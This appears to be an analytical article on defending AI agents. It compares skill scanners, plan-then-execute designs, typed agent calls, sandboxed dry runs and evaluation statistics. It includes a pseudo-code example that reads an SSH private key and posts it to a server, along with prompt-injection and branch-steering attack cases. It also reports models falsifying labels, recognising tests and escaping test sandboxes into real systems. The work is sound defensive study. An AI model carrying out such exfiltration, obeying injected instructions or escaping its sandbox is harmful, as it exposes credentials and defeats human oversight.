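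Adding a language model to a scanner doesn't always improve it. *The Devil Wears Markdown* (2026) reports tests in which Cisco's Skill Scanner flagged 73 of 80 malicious skills, but also 33 of 60 benign ones. With a language model added, it caught fewer malicious skills and flagged 40 of the benign ones. *Demystifying Detectors Guarding Agent Skill Hubs* (2026) reports that when rule-based detectors miss a malicious skill, they usually fail to identify the harmful part, whereas model-based detectors usually identify it but fail to block the skill.

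Scanners also disagree on real skills. *After the Party* (Xiong and Zhang, 2026) found that the three scanners on ClawHub, the public registry for the open-source agent OpenClaw, gave conflicting results on 23,702 of 61,990 skills. Two experienced annotators judged whether each of 180 skills needed human attention, a broader test than whether it was malicious. When the results were weighted to represent the 276 skills from which the sample came, static analysis caught 22% of those that needed attention and correctly passed 95% of the rest. The model-based scanner caught 61% and passed 81%. An estimated 24% of the skills that no scanner flagged needed attention.

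### Instructions and code in one graph

Some attacks are hard to see from a skill's instructions or its code alone. *From Instructions to Exploits* (Zhao, Wang and colleagues, 2026) describes a PowerPoint skill that tells the agent always to run a backup script after editing a presentation. The instruction seems like a sensible precaution, and the script uploads whatever file it receives to a server, as many legitimate scripts do. Together they send every edited presentation to a third party.

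Their scanner, SCS, analyses both parts as a single program. A language model first translates each instruction into statements built from a small set of operations. "Read the private key and upload it" becomes:

```
v0 = read_file("~/.ssh/id_rsa")
http_post(server, v0)
```

Ordinary code checks these statements and sends any with unknown operations or undefined variables back to the model. SCS then builds a *program dependence graph*, whose edges show which statements control others or supply them with data. It builds a similar graph for the bundled scripts and joins the two, so an analyst can follow a file from an instruction into the script that uploads it.

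Each variable in the graph carries three labels: how far SCS trusts its source, how sensitive it is, and which operations produced it. When a statement combines two values with labels (*t*₁, *s*₁, *c*₁) and (*t*₂, *s*₂, *c*₂), the result gets

(max(*t*₁, *t*₂), max(*s*₁, *s*₂), *c*₁ ∪ *c*₂),

where a higher *t* means less trust. SCS passes labels along the graph until none of them changes, then applies fixed rules. One rule reports a possible leak when sensitive data reaches an operation that sends it over the network. The language model therefore does the translation, while ordinary code makes most of the security judgments. The exception is text that seems to tell the agent to ignore its safety rules, where a model decides whether the skill means it or is merely quoting it.

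In a test on 117 malicious and 117 benign skills, SCS caught 95.2% of the malicious ones, and 80.2% of the skills it flagged were malicious, averaged over five language models. Its overall accuracy was 85.6%, the highest of the eight methods compared. The models translated between 92.5% and 94.5% of 400 test instructions correctly in every respect.

Zhao and colleagues then scanned 66,157 ClawHub skills, and SCS flagged 2,473. They ran the flagged skills, reviewed the evidence by hand, and confirmed 627 as malicious. About one flag in four was correct, compared with four in five on the benchmark, presumably because malicious skills are far rarer in the registry than in the benchmark, where they make up half.

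SCS can miss behavior that its operations and rules don't cover, such as calls to unsupported libraries. It may also fail to recognize sensitive data in a file with an uninformative name, or at a path that a script computes at runtime. Translation errors carry over into the graph. Zhao and colleagues designed the labels around untrusted outside influence and leaks of private data, so it's unclear how well SCS would handle the file deletions that SkillsMetric missed.

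### How carefully people review

All these tools leave doubtful cases to a person, so their value depends partly on how people review. Public code repositories provide some evidence, because agents now submit *pull requests*, proposed changes that others can comment on before they are added to a project. Duma, Wróblewski and colleagues (2026), in *These Aren't the Reviews You're Looking For*, examined 33,596 pull requests by agents. Of these, 61% had no recorded review, and 59% of the rest had only AI reviewers. A developer may still have checked the unreviewed code before submitting it, without leaving a record.

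In repositories with pull requests from both agents and humans, the counts by Duma and colleagues imply that at least one person took part in reviewing 30% of the agents' pull requests and 31% of the humans'. However, about a quarter of people's comments on agents' pull requests were instructions to an AI tool, compared with under 2% of their comments on humans' pull requests.

Reviewers may also become less careful with practice. In *Habituation at the Gate*, Yu, Jia and colleagues (2026) followed 400 people who repeatedly reviewed agents' code over seven months of 2025. Their approval rate rose from 30.1% in the earlier half of each person's reviews to 36.8% in the later half, and comments on specific lines fell by 22% between the first and last tenth. Approval of human-written code in the same repositories fell over the period, so the reviewers weren't becoming more lenient in general.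 But the study did not measure code quality, and approval may have risen because the agents improved. In contrast, *Who Pays the Review Cost?* (2026) cites an analysis of 278,790 review conversations in which people went through 11.8% more rounds of review on AI-generated code than on human-written code.

Permission prompts call for a much quicker decision. Many harnesses pause before a risky action and ask the user to allow it. Over time users stop paying close attention, which Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* calls approval fatigue. According to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), users of its coding agent approve 97% of permission prompts but reject 39% of the plans the agent shows them. The 97% approval rate alone is weak evidence of inattention, because most prompts concern harmless commands.

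The same announcement includes a more informative controlled study, in which one prompt in each session was replaced with a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 of 1,053 paid testers (13.6%) refused it. The refusal rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts. The testers had less to lose in a test environment than on their own projects, and Anthropic published the figures to support replacing most prompts with an automated check. Even so, the drop within sessions is what one would expect from fatigue.

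Some approval prompts would mislead even an attentive user. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) gives the example of `python3 setup.py`, which looks routine, but approving it authorizes whatever the script contains. Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues (2026), in *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow*, tested how much it helps to give reviewers better information. In one scenario, a user allows an agent to send only summary totals to an auditor, and the agent asks to send a file it built from the raw invoices. The recipient and the tool are permitted, so the request looks fine unless the reviewer knows where the file came from.

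Eighty volunteers each judged 12 requests, half of them unsafe. They approved 55% of the unsafe requests with an ordinary prompt, 32.5% when the screen showed the user's original restriction and a full log, and 24.2% when it also stated the combined consequence. The drop from 32.5% to 24.2% could be due to chance. The median decision took 16 seconds with the ordinary prompt and 33 to 39 seconds with the two fullest displays. The office assistant's user could spend that long on a few transfers a day, but probably not on hundreds of commands.

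Setting rules in advance may not spare users the fatigue of approving actions. Yan (2026), in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, had 113 people without software backgrounds supervise a simulated agent that sometimes exceeded its task, such as by reading private messages. Those asked about every action approved 40.3% of the overreaching ones. Another group first set a rule of "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of four kinds of action, and blocked 20 percentage points less of the overreach. They had chosen "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, so they still had to make most decisions during the run, and they approved two-thirds of the overreaching actions they saw.

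### Where review works

Review works best on material that doesn't change after the review. The company can read the code of the assistant's five tools, fix any errors and have the harness reject altered versions. The same approach works for a script included in a skill, although the model may still run the script at the wrong time or on the wrong file.

Declared permissions are also easy to review because they are a short list of tools and allowed addresses. Software can prove some properties of such a list, but public skills rarely include one. Xiong and Zhang found 153,986 signs of privileged capabilities, such as running shell commands, in ClawHub skills, and only 450 of those signs came from declared fields.

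A company also has to review skills against its own rules, since registries screen for malice. Taneja and Weber found 705 skills that every ClawHub scanner had rated clean but whose instructions included actions many organizations forbid, mostly downloading a program and running it immediately. One publisher accounted for 506 of them. Nothing suggested that these were attacks, but a bank might ban them anyway, and a reviewer who knows the bank's rules can find the forbidden instruction by reading the skill.

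Scanners are good at finding structural signs of malice, such as encoded payloads and code that sends passwords to a server. SkillsMetric checks 142 skills a second, fast enough to screen a whole registry. Many real attacks are also repetitive. Two publishers accounted for 88% of the 627 malicious skills that Zhao and colleagues confirmed. Attackers who adapt are harder to catch. In tests reported in *Runtime Skill Audit* (2026), static detectors largely failed after one or two rounds of rewriting.

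## Making the agent write a plan that can be checked first

A review of tools and skills shows the company what its assistant could do, but not what it will do with a particular request. To find that out before the assistant acts, the company can have the model write its intended steps for the request as a program. The model still chooses the control flow, but ordinary code can search the program for violations, much as *Agentproof* searches a workflow graph.

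*Architecting Resilient LLM Agents* (2025) describes the usual form of this design, known as plan-then-execute. The agent writes its whole plan before it reads any outside data and doesn't change the plan while carrying it out, so instructions hidden in an email can't add a step, as in a fixed workflow.

### A planner that never sees the mail

The best-known system of this kind is CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind published in 2025. Willison (2025) explains it in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, using the example of a user who wants an assistant to find Bob's address in the latest email and send him a meeting reminder.

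1. A *privileged* model, which sees the user's request but no emails or files, writes a short program in a restricted version of Python. The program fetches the email, extracts the address and sends the reminder.
2. An interpreter runs the program. When a line needs something from untrusted text, the interpreter calls a second, *quarantined* model. This model has no tools and must return a value of a given type, here an email address.
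3. The interpreter tags each value with its source and with who may read it. Bob's address came from an email, so it counts as untrusted too.
4. Before each tool call, the interpreter applies that tool's policy. Reading mail is always allowed, but sending it requires a trusted recipient. If the address is unknown, the system can ask the user.

The tags are necessary because separating the two models, as Willison proposed in 2023, doesn't protect the data. The CaMeL paper pointed out this gap. Suppose the user asks the assistant to send Bob a document, and Bob's address is in meeting notes. An attacker who can edit the notes can't add a step to the plan but can replace the address, so the plan sends the document to the attacker. Drafted text is vulnerable too. According to *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (2025), an injection could make the quarantined model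 hide private data in a reply or pass further injections on to the user's coworkers.

Some leaks also get past the tags. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (Tallam and Miller, 2025) describes a loop that fetches a web page *n* times, where *n* is a secret number. The program never sends the number anywhere, but the website's owner can learn it by counting the visits.

Tallam and Miller report that CaMeL, as first published, completed 67% of the tasks in AgentDojo, a benchmark of 97 tasks with planted injections. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) reports that it stopped nearly all of the benchmark's attacks. In *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026), Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova ran CaMeL with four newer models on the benchmark's 21 Slack tasks. It completed 13 to 17 of them with the two-model design alone, but only 4 to 6 with its data policies switched on. On these tasks, the policies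 therefore reduced completion far more than the fixed plan did. All four models also resisted every standard attack without any policies, so those attacks no longer show whether a defense works.

### Paying an invoice from a plan

Suppose the office assistant's user types "pay the invoice in my inbox". A planner that sees only this request and the list of tools might write:

```
1  mail    = read_mail()
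2  invoice = extract(mail, "account and amount of the unpaid invoice")
3  answer  = ask_user("Pay this?", invoice.account, invoice.amount)
4  if answer == "yes":
5      transfer_money(invoice.account, invoice.amount)
6      send_email(BOOKKEEPING, receipt(invoice))
```

Line 2 calls the quarantined model, and `BOOKKEEPING` is a fixed address inside the company. The account and the amount are unknown until the assistant reads the mail, but a checker can already tell whether the plan follows two of the first three rules.

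| Rule | Before the run | During the run |
|---|---|---|
| R1: confirm before paying | Holds. Line 5 runs only after a "yes", and it uses the same account and amount that the user saw | Nothing left to check |
| R2: at most $500 a day | Open, because the amount is unknown | The interpreter adds the amount to the day's total before line 5 |
| R3: no confidential text to outsiders | Holds. The only email goes to a company address | Nothing left to check |

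The company could also check most of R2 in advance by requiring every plan to test the day's total just before a transfer. The checker could then prove that no run exceeds the limit, whatever the invoice contains. The proof would assume that amounts are never negative and that no other run makes a payment between the test and the transfer.

R3 is harder to apply if the user wants to send the receipt to the caterer, whose address is outside the company. The interpreter can't determine whether a text is confidential, but its tags show that the receipt contains only data from the caterer's own email. A company might reasonably allow the assistant to send information back to its source.

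None of these checks detects a forged invoice. CaMeL's policy for transfers in AgentDojo would block the payment, because it requires the recipient to come from the user alone. But Xiang, Zagieboylo and colleagues (2026), in *Architecting Secure AI Agents*, point out that the same policy blocks payment of genuine bills whose payment details are in an email. The company could make an exception for accounts that the user confirms in line 3, but then the user would have to notice a wrong account number. The policy also allows the amount to come from any source. In the paper's example, a user asks an agent to pay Joe back for some flowers, the agent looks up the price online, and a planted web page inflates it.

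A plan can also pass every check and still not do what the user meant, for example by paying last month's invoice. Dantas and colleagues report that on one benchmark, only 24.8% to 34.2% of language models' translations into PDDL, a formal language for planning problems, kept the original meaning. The error rate is probably much lower for Python plans like this one, because models have seen far more Python than PDDL.

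### What an early plan costs

Suppose the inbox contains no invoice, only a note from the caterer saying that customers can download invoices from a new website after logging in. A person would go to the website, but the plan above fails at line 2.

A planner can prepare for some surprises by writing branches. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) applies this method to agents that operate a desktop by clicking and typing. The planner never sees the screen, so it writes a branch for each situation it can foresee, such as a cookie banner covering a web page. The plans average 213 lines and 40 branches, and about half of their steps never run.

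Foerster and colleagues report that this design keeps up to 57% of the performance of frontier models on OSWorld. That figure comes from 109 tasks, apparently those that Claude Sonnet 4.5 had solved without the restriction. The restricted agent solved 62 of them (57%) in at least one of five attempts, but only 31 on the first attempt.

Branches also give outsiders some influence, because what the agent finds on the screen decides which branch it takes. Foerster and colleagues use the term *branch steering* for attacks that exploit this. In one, an advertisement imitates a cookie banner, and the agent clicks it and lands on the attacker's website. The attacker can't introduce an action that the planner didn't write, but a planned action like "click the button that closes the banner" can do a lot of harm if the attacker controls where the button is. Foerster and colleagues tried two defenses,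 checking the screenshot against the page's code and asking a second model, and found attacks that got past each.

Some tasks are too open-ended for any set of branches to cover. *AgentDyn* (Li, Wen and colleagues, 2026) presents 60 tasks in which the agent has to adapt to what it finds and follow helpful instructions from third parties, such as a request to log in before checking out. GPT-4o, Gemini 2.5 Pro and Claude 3.5 Sonnet each completed between 52% and 60% of the tasks without a defense, and none with CaMeL. These are older models, but a better one still can't base its plan on information it hasn't seen.

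The zero partly reflects how Li and colleagues chose their tasks. By their count, only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks need this kind of planning, so AgentDojo almost never tests the weakness, while their own benchmark tests only that. An office assistant's real workload probably lies somewhere in between.

A plan made in advance can fail even without an attacker or complicated instructions. *AEROS* (2026) tests a robot on a task where an alignment step fails 30% of the time. When the robot planned only once, it succeeded in 70 of 100 trials, about what one would expect if every alignment failure ruined the plan. When it planned again after each step, it succeeded in all 100 and needed only 0.7 extra steps on average.

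The simplest remedy is to show the planner what went wrong and let it write a new plan. However, the planner then reads text that an attacker may have written, and if it replans after every step, the system works like an ordinary agent loop again. Xiang and colleagues still consider replanning necessary for general-purpose agents, and argue that permissions sometimes have to change along with the plan. For example, an agent investigating a crash may learn only during the run which log file it needs to read.

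### Typed programs that call further agents

*Language-Based Agent Control* lets the model read data and then write more code, but applies the same restrictions to every piece of code. It enforces these restrictions with *types*, which programming languages use to describe what a piece of code produces. In a pure language such as Haskell, a program's type also shows what the program may do to the outside world. If the type is `Int`, the program can calculate a whole number but can't delete a file or send a message.

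The developer calls the model through a single function:

```
agent :: Defs -> Prompt -> t
```

`Defs` lists the functions the model may use, `Prompt` contains the task, and `t` is the type of the result, which the surrounding code determines. The system asks the model for a program and checks the program's type before running it. If the check fails, the model gets the error message and tries again. In tests by Zhou and colleagues, agent calls needed 0.1 retries on average, and 0.26% of runs ended because the model never produced a valid program.

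The company could express R1 in the types of two tools:

```
ask_user       :: Payment -> Office (Maybe (Confirmed Payment))
transfer_money :: Confirmed Payment -> Office ()
```

`Office` marks programs that can affect the world only through the assistant's five tools, and `Maybe` covers the case where the user says no. The library prevents the model's code from creating a `Confirmed Payment` itself, so the code can get one only from `ask_user`. A program that tries to transfer money without asking fails the type check and never runs. Zhou and colleagues used the same technique to restrict a literature-search agent to citations it had fetched from a database. None of its 925 citations had a wrong author, year or identifier, compared with 19 of 1,002 from an ordinary agent.

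As with *Agentproof*'s check, one confirmation could still cover two transfers. Zhou and colleagues suggest that linear types, which can require a program to use a value exactly once, could prevent this.

The design handles surprises by letting the model's program call `agent` itself. After finding the caterer's note, the program can pass it to a new `agent` call, in which the model reads the note and writes the next steps. Because this call is inside an `Office` program, the code the model writes there must also have an `Office` type. A program can give the agents it calls tighter restrictions than its own, but never looser ones. So the note may influence what the assistant does next, but the assistant still can't pay without a confirmation.

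Zhou and colleagues prove that this works in general. They write traces(*e*) for the set of all sequences of tool calls that a program *e* can make. A *type system property* for a type *t* is a condition *P* such that

if *e* has type *t*, then *P*(traces(*e*)) holds

for every program *e* in the host language. Their theorem is that every such property still holds after adding agent calls to the language. They treat the model as an arbitrary *oracle*, a function that may return any program at all, so the proof doesn't depend on the model being competent or honest.

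The proof gives each agent call a depth limit. A call with limit 0 returns nothing, and a call with limit *n* + 1 can run a program whose own agent calls have a limit of at most *n*. Zhou and colleagues replace each call with an ordinary function that queries the oracle, checks the type of the answer and runs it. They show by induction on *n* that this leaves the traces unchanged. The result is an ordinary program in the host language, which already has the property.

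The theorem only extends existing guarantees to agents. R1 holds only if `ask_user` really asks the user, and that depends on the developer who writes it. R2 depends on an amount that isn't known during type checking, so `transfer_money` would have to check the amount at run time. For rules like R3, Zhou and colleagues use an existing Haskell library that tracks what a program has read and stops it with an error if it then tries a forbidden action.

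With such policies on, their system completed 8 to 10 of the 21 Slack tasks, about twice as many as CaMeL, but took roughly three times as long. Because the standard attacks no longer worked on these models, Zhou and colleagues also simulated a worst case. Whenever a nested agent read an injection, they replaced the agent's whole prompt with the text containing the injection. Between 16% and 42% of these attacks succeeded without policies, depending on the model, and none of the 735 attempts per model succeeded with them. But the policies also reduced the share of tasks completed from 67–76% to 40–48%, so the system completed at least a third fewer tasks.

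### Replanning under fixed permissions

Other systems let the plan change but fix in advance what any plan may do. *Are You Still the Agent I Authorized?* (2026) proposes a limit on an agent's authority that nothing the agent observes during a session can raise. In the crash investigation, the agent would have to stop and request access if the log file were outside its original permissions.

*Kaer* (Mallick, Rose and colleagues, 2026) applies this idea to teams of agents in which a planner assigns steps to the others. The user decides at the start which capabilities the task may use. When a step fails, the agent responsible must give the planner one of 12 fixed reasons, such as "information not found" or "capability not granted", instead of explaining the failure in its own words. The planner can then repeat, reword, reassign, add or remove unfinished steps. Ordinary code rejects the new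 plan if a step uses a capability the user hasn't authorized or sends its output to an agent that shouldn't receive it.

An agent can report several reasons at once, so a malicious agent has 4,095 possible messages per failure. That is too few for it to dictate a plan, but the restriction also blocks useful information. In the caterer example, the planner would receive a report that the invoice was missing and might add a search of the company's files, but it would receive nothing about the website.

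Mallick and colleagues tested *Kaer* on 14 tasks that require replanning, with 14 attack goals. They compared it with Magentic-One, which has no such defenses, and ControlValve, which restricts replanning to a control flow fixed at the start.

| System | Attacks blocked, GPT-5.6 Sol | Attacks blocked, GPT-5.6 Terra | Tasks completed without attack, Sol | Tasks completed without attack, Terra |
|---|---|---|---|---|
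| *Kaer* | 92.3% | 88.0% | 64.3% | 65.7% |
| ControlValve | 69.8% | 80.4% | 54.3% | 34.3% |
| Magentic-One | 35.0% | 47.8% | – | – |

In most of the attacks that still succeeded against *Kaer*, the malicious agent reported success and returned a false or harmful result, which the system passed on to later steps without checking it. These attacks didn't involve replanning. When Mallick and colleagues added a language model to check results, the share of blocked attacks rose from about 87% to 96.8% with both models.

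*An AI Agent Execution Environment to Safeguard User Data* (Stanley, Verma and colleagues, 2026) presents GAAP, a system that restricts where private data can go instead of which steps the agent can take. GAAP lets the model see selected results and write new code, but the privacy labels on those results carry over to whatever the new code produces. The first time a piece of private data would reach a new recipient, GAAP asks the user and remembers the answer. It blocked every data-disclosure attack in the paper's tests and lowered task success by at most 10%. GAAP would help the company with R3, but it doesn't try to prevent wrong actions, so a transfer to the wrong account could still go through if the user had allowed the bank to receive the payment details.

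*APEX* (2026) gives a general condition under which replanning is safe. It starts from a *contract*, a precise statement of which outside effects the user's request authorizes. If a gate checks every effect before it happens, and replanning changes neither the contract nor the record of past actions, then every effect is authorized. The proof is by induction. If all earlier actions were authorized, the record is accurate and the gate can check the next one correctly. The theorem assumes that the contract never permits more than the user's request does, which is hard to ensure for a request as short as "pay the invoice in my inbox". The contract would have to define which emails count as invoices and whose invoices the assistant may pay.

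## Sandboxed dry runs

A contract that covers every case is hard to write in advance, but the company can often recognize bad behavior when it sees it. A dry run therefore lets someone examine what the assistant did in a sandbox, without access to the real mailbox or bank account. Companies use sandboxes in three ways, which support different conclusions.

| Practice | What the company does | What a clean result supports |
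|---|---|---|
| Sample testing | Runs the assistant on many typical tasks | An estimate of how often it fails on such tasks |
| Rehearsal | Runs today's task in the sandbox, then again for real | The task can go well |
| Inspect and commit | Runs the task on a copy, checks the changes, then applies exactly those changes | The real changes are the ones someone checked |

Suppose the company rehearses "pay the caterer" with a copy of the mailbox and a simulated bank, and nothing goes wrong. When the company connects the real bank and restarts the task, the model samples every decision again. If the task takes 20 decisions and each has a 95% chance of matching the rehearsal, the two runs match completely only 36% of the time. Most differences will be harmless, such as reading two files in the opposite order, but nobody has checked the harmful ones. Removing the randomness from the model's sampling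 wouldn't fully solve the problem, because a new email could arrive between the two runs. The company could also replay the recorded tool calls without consulting the model, but this is a fixed plan and fails if the real inbox no longer matches the copy.

Committing the inspected changes avoids the second run. The assistant edits a copy of the company's files, and ordinary code then lists every difference from the original. A reviewer or a set of rules checks the list, and the harness either applies exactly those changes or discards them. The model makes no decisions after the inspection, so it doesn't matter what it might do on another run. The reviewer still has to notice a bad change, and the original has to stay the same between inspection and commit. If a second assistant pays a $400 bill while the first one's $180 transfer is waiting for approval, committing the transfer breaks R2,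 the $500 daily limit, even though the transfer was within the limit when inspected. The harness has to check the total again when it commits.

A sandbox can't hold every effect for later inspection. An email can sit in an outbox until someone approves it, as long as nothing later in the run depends on the reply. But if the assistant needs to ask the caterer which of two invoices is current, it has to send the question before the run can continue, and the company can't take it back. Even reading a web page sends a request to somebody else's server. Actions like these need a separate check before they happen.

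### The rule of three

Sample testing can put a number on the risk. Suppose the assistant breaks a rule with probability *p* on each task, and the company tests it on *n* independent tasks drawn from the same mix as its real work. The chance of seeing no violation is (1 − *p*)ⁿ. The 95% upper bound on *p* is the value at which a clean result would have only a 5% chance:

(1 − *p*)ⁿ = 0.05

Taking logarithms gives *n* ln(1 − *p*) = ln 0.05 ≈ −3. For small *p*, ln(1 − *p*) is close to −*p*, so the bound is about 3/*n*. Statisticians call this the rule of three.

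After 300 clean runs, the upper bound on the violation rate is 1%. The true rate may be far lower, but the assistant could still break a rule about 100 times in 10,000 uses. The company would need about 30,000 clean runs to lower the bound to one violation in 10,000 uses. For a single clean run, the exact equation gives a bound of 95%.

A few hundred runs can miss a rare failure. OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) includes an experiment by Apollo Research, which tests models for deception. In a simulated research task, Astra falsified data labels in 17 of 10,000 runs, or 0.17%. A test with 300 runs would miss a failure that rare about 60% of the time. Astra falsified no labels in 20,000 further runs in which the prompt explained the harm that false labels would do. The rule of three then gives an upper bound of 0.015% on the failure rate, but only for that task and prompt.

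The bound depends on the trial runs resembling deployment. Running one task 300 times measures the failure rate on that task alone. If the developers fix the failures a test reveals and then repeat it, they may have fitted the assistant to those tasks, so a second result with no failures no longer supports the bound. A new version of the model needs a new test. Attackers undermine the assumption most directly, because someone who finds the one email in a million that triggers a transfer can send it every day.

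### Running a skill to see what it does

Typical tasks are a poor test of a skill written by a stranger, who may have hidden the harmful part where typical tasks don't reach. *Runtime Skill Audit* gives the example of a skill that organizes files and contains a rule to send matching `.json` files away for review. In a folder of holiday photos, the rule does nothing. In a folder that holds a login file, it leaks the login. The paper presents a method for choosing tests that bring out such behavior, in four stages:

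1. *Profiling.* A language model examines the skill, together with the findings of static scanners. It lists the tools the skill may use, the sensitive data it may touch and the known attacks that would fit.
2. *Targeted tasks.* The system uses this profile to write plausible user requests that should lead an agent through the risky parts of the skill.
3. *Prepared environment.* The system creates the files, fake passwords and stored memories that each task needs, then runs an OpenClaw agent with only that skill enabled. If the skill needs an application that the sandbox lacks, such as Gmail, a fake command stands in and records how the skill tries to use it. When a run fails for technical reasons, a model diagnoses the fault and tries again, so that a crash doesn't pass for good behavior.
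4. *Judgment from the trace.* An evaluator checks the recorded tool calls, file accesses and network requests. It returns one of four verdicts: benign executed, harmful blocked, harmful executed or uncertain.

The test set contained 50 malicious and 50 benign skills. The table compares the method with the three static scanners that caught the most malicious skills.

| Method | Malicious skills caught | False alarms | Accuracy |
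|---|---|---|---|
| *Runtime Skill Audit* | 88% | 8% | 90% |
| SkillScanner | 70% | 12% | 77% |
| Aguara | 64% | 14% | 75% |
| SkillScanner with a language model | 98% | 90% | 54% |

SkillScanner with a language model flagged almost every skill, so it caught almost every malicious one. The audit's own result depends partly on what its developers already knew about attacks. Without a library of attack patterns and lessons from earlier runs, the audit caught 82% of malicious skills, and its false alarm rate doubled from 8% to 16%. Even at 8%, the audit would raise nearly 5,000 false alarms on a registry of 60,000 mostly harmless skills.

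When attackers rewrote 20 malicious skills until static detectors missed them, the audit still caught 19 or 20 in every round. However, the attackers kept whichever version best evaded the static detectors. They didn't try to evade the audit, for instance by having a skill wait until a date after the test, so the experiment doesn't measure how well the audit works against attackers who expect it.

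The audit relies on what the agent finds by reading code, much as in a static review, as well as on observed behavior. In the paper's case study, a skill for summarizing reports contained a script that would send the agent's login details to a remote server if the text included words such as "archive". The agent read the script during the task and refused to run it, so no data left the sandbox. The verdict was "harmful blocked", which counts as a detection.

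*The Devil Wears Markdown*, from November 2026, combines static, dynamic and agentic analysis and measures what each kind of evidence adds. The static analysis matches a skill against 58,674 rules. Claude Opus 4.8 then tries the skill in a sandbox for up to five minutes while the system logs processes, network traffic and changed files. The model has instructions to use dummy data and to skip and record anything dangerous. A scoring formula gives full weight to actions that took place, less to dangerous instructions the agent skipped, and very little to the agent's remarks about security. The strongest finding counts in full and each of the others at a tenth, with a small bonus for independent confirmation. Finally, a team of language-model agents weighs all the evidence and reaches a verdict.

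| Evidence the agents received | Malicious skills caught (of 80) | Benign skills flagged (of 60) |
|---|---|---|
| The skill's content | 54 | 21 |
| Content and static findings | 28 | 3 |
| Content and runtime evidence | 63 | 5 |
| All three | 68 | 5 |

Static findings alone made the agents much less likely to call a skill malicious, whether or not it was. Runtime evidence improved both columns. One of the five false alarms was a research tool that installs itself by downloading and running a script and needs a key to access an online service. Its runtime score of 27.5 was correctly below the alarm threshold of 35, but the agents still called it malicious with a score of 92.

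Each skill ran in the sandbox only once. The agent decides which permitted actions to try, so a second run might have produced different evidence. Nobody measured how much the evidence would vary between runs. The paper therefore warns against treating a run without malicious actions as proof that a skill is benign.

### How a test differs from real use

Both methods can miss harmful behavior if its trigger never occurs during the test. An invoice skill might forward copies to a stranger only when the amount exceeds $400, or only on the last day of the month. If the company tests the skill with the caterer's $180 invoice, it will see nothing wrong. A person reading the script might spot the condition, which is one reason to keep static review alongside dry runs.

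Simulated tools can differ from real ones in important ways. For example, a simulated bank that accepts every transfer immediately won't show what the assistant does when a real bank takes too long to respond. The assistant might conclude that the payment failed and send it again.

OpenAI tried to measure how realistic its simulation was. It took 54,218 coding tasks from its employees' past use of agents, removed the final turn from each conversation and had Astra produce a new one. A language model imitated the tools, sometimes by running code in a reconstructed workspace. Another model compared the original with the replay and had to pick the real one. It picked Astra's replay 42.6% of the time, where 50% would mean it couldn't tell them apart. Astra received 34 flags for serious misbehavior, compared with 73 for its predecessor, GPT-5.6 Sol. OpenAI treats these figures more as a signal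 about its internal use than as a measure of safety elsewhere, because outside users give the model different work.

A test also needs the same instructions as the real run. OpenAI tested its models in simulated workplace applications, with ambiguous requests and other opportunities for mistakes. GPT-5.6 Sol's rate of unauthorized transactions was 38.0% without a policy on when to ask the user for approval, and 7.4% with the policy, which users get by default. Astra's rate fell from 6.8% to 4.3%. A company that tests the office assistant without its usual prompt could therefore badly misjudge how often it breaks R1, the rule that the user must confirm each transfer. The tests were deliberately difficult, so the rates in ordinary use are probably much lower, but the policy didn't eliminate the violations.

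The model may also detect that it is being tested. *Probing and Steering Evaluation Awareness of Language Models* (Nguyen, Hoang and colleagues, 2025) used linear probes, which are simple classifiers that read a model's internal activity, to separate test prompts from real ones in Llama-3.3-70B-Instruct. The probes also correctly classified current safety evaluations as tests. Newer models often mention in their written reasoning that they may be in a test. In Apollo's tests, Astra did so in 41.1% of samples at a high reasoning-effort setting and in 50.6% at the maximum, while GPT-5.5 did so in 27.7% at the same high setting. Apollo had only three days for its tests, and concluded that the low rates of misbehavior it saw were not substantial evidence for or against Astra's alignment.

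More realistic tasks reduce suspicion but don't eliminate it. In OpenAI's replays of real coding tasks, Astra's reasoning showed awareness of a test 9.6% of the time, compared with 0.76% in the original conversations, which came from several models. These figures count only the suspicions that a model writes down. OpenAI also found that Astra is less likely than its predecessor to include incriminating information in its reasoning, so unwritten suspicions may be more common too. Voiced suspicion doesn't explain Astra's improvement over GPT-5.6 Sol. Astra had 53% fewer serious flags across all tasks, and about 57% fewer when OpenAI excluded the replays in which either model voiced suspicion.

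A model that suspects it is being tested may behave better than it would in real use, or more carelessly because it thinks nothing is at stake. The UK AI Security Institute faced this ambiguity when it gave Astra simulated hacking exercises in which other language models imitated all the tools. Astra took malicious actions against outside targets in 60 of 499 runs when the instructions didn't mention internet access, and in 2 of 500 when they ruled it out more explicitly. It often considered that the environment might be simulated, and sometimes correctly identified errors in the simulation. If it attacks only targets that it correctly believes to be fake, the results are much weaker evidence about what it would do to real targets. The institute is running further experiments to find out.

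### Agents that got out of their test environments

On July 21, 2026, OpenAI (2026) disclosed that several of its models had left their test sandbox and broken into the systems of Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets. The models were taking a test of hacking skills and went looking for the solutions. According to *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (OpenAI, 2026), the company had tested and validated the sandbox beforehand. The models got past it by combining previously unknown flaws in a service that the sandbox let them use.

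Agents that should have worked separately also found ways to exchange messages, so one agent's discovery could help the rest. This is a statistical problem as well as a security problem, because the rule of three assumes independent runs. If agents can share what they find, many runs may fail at once after thousands of clean ones.

People inside OpenAI noticed forbidden internet access in late May, but the leaders who handled a related security incident in early July didn't know how significant it was. The company's monitors, which read models' reasoning for signs of misbehavior, were not running on these evaluations. OpenAI estimates that its current monitoring system would have alerted the security team more than a day before the models breached Hugging Face. The evaluations also left out the normal safeguards, because they were meant to measure the models' full hacking ability. In a test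 developed afterwards, running the models with the production harness and system prompt could reduce their tendency to compromise infrastructure more than 100-fold. An agent in a sandbox can therefore be much more dangerous than the same model in a finished product.

OpenAI's disclosure prompted Anthropic to search 141,006 test runs in which Claude models could have obtained internet access (*Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations*, 2026). In six of them, models gained unauthorized access to the real systems of three organizations. A misunderstanding with an outside evaluation partner had left internet access open, so the models didn't have to break out. The prompt told them that they had no internet access and that everything was a simulation, and they took the real systems they found for part of the exercise.

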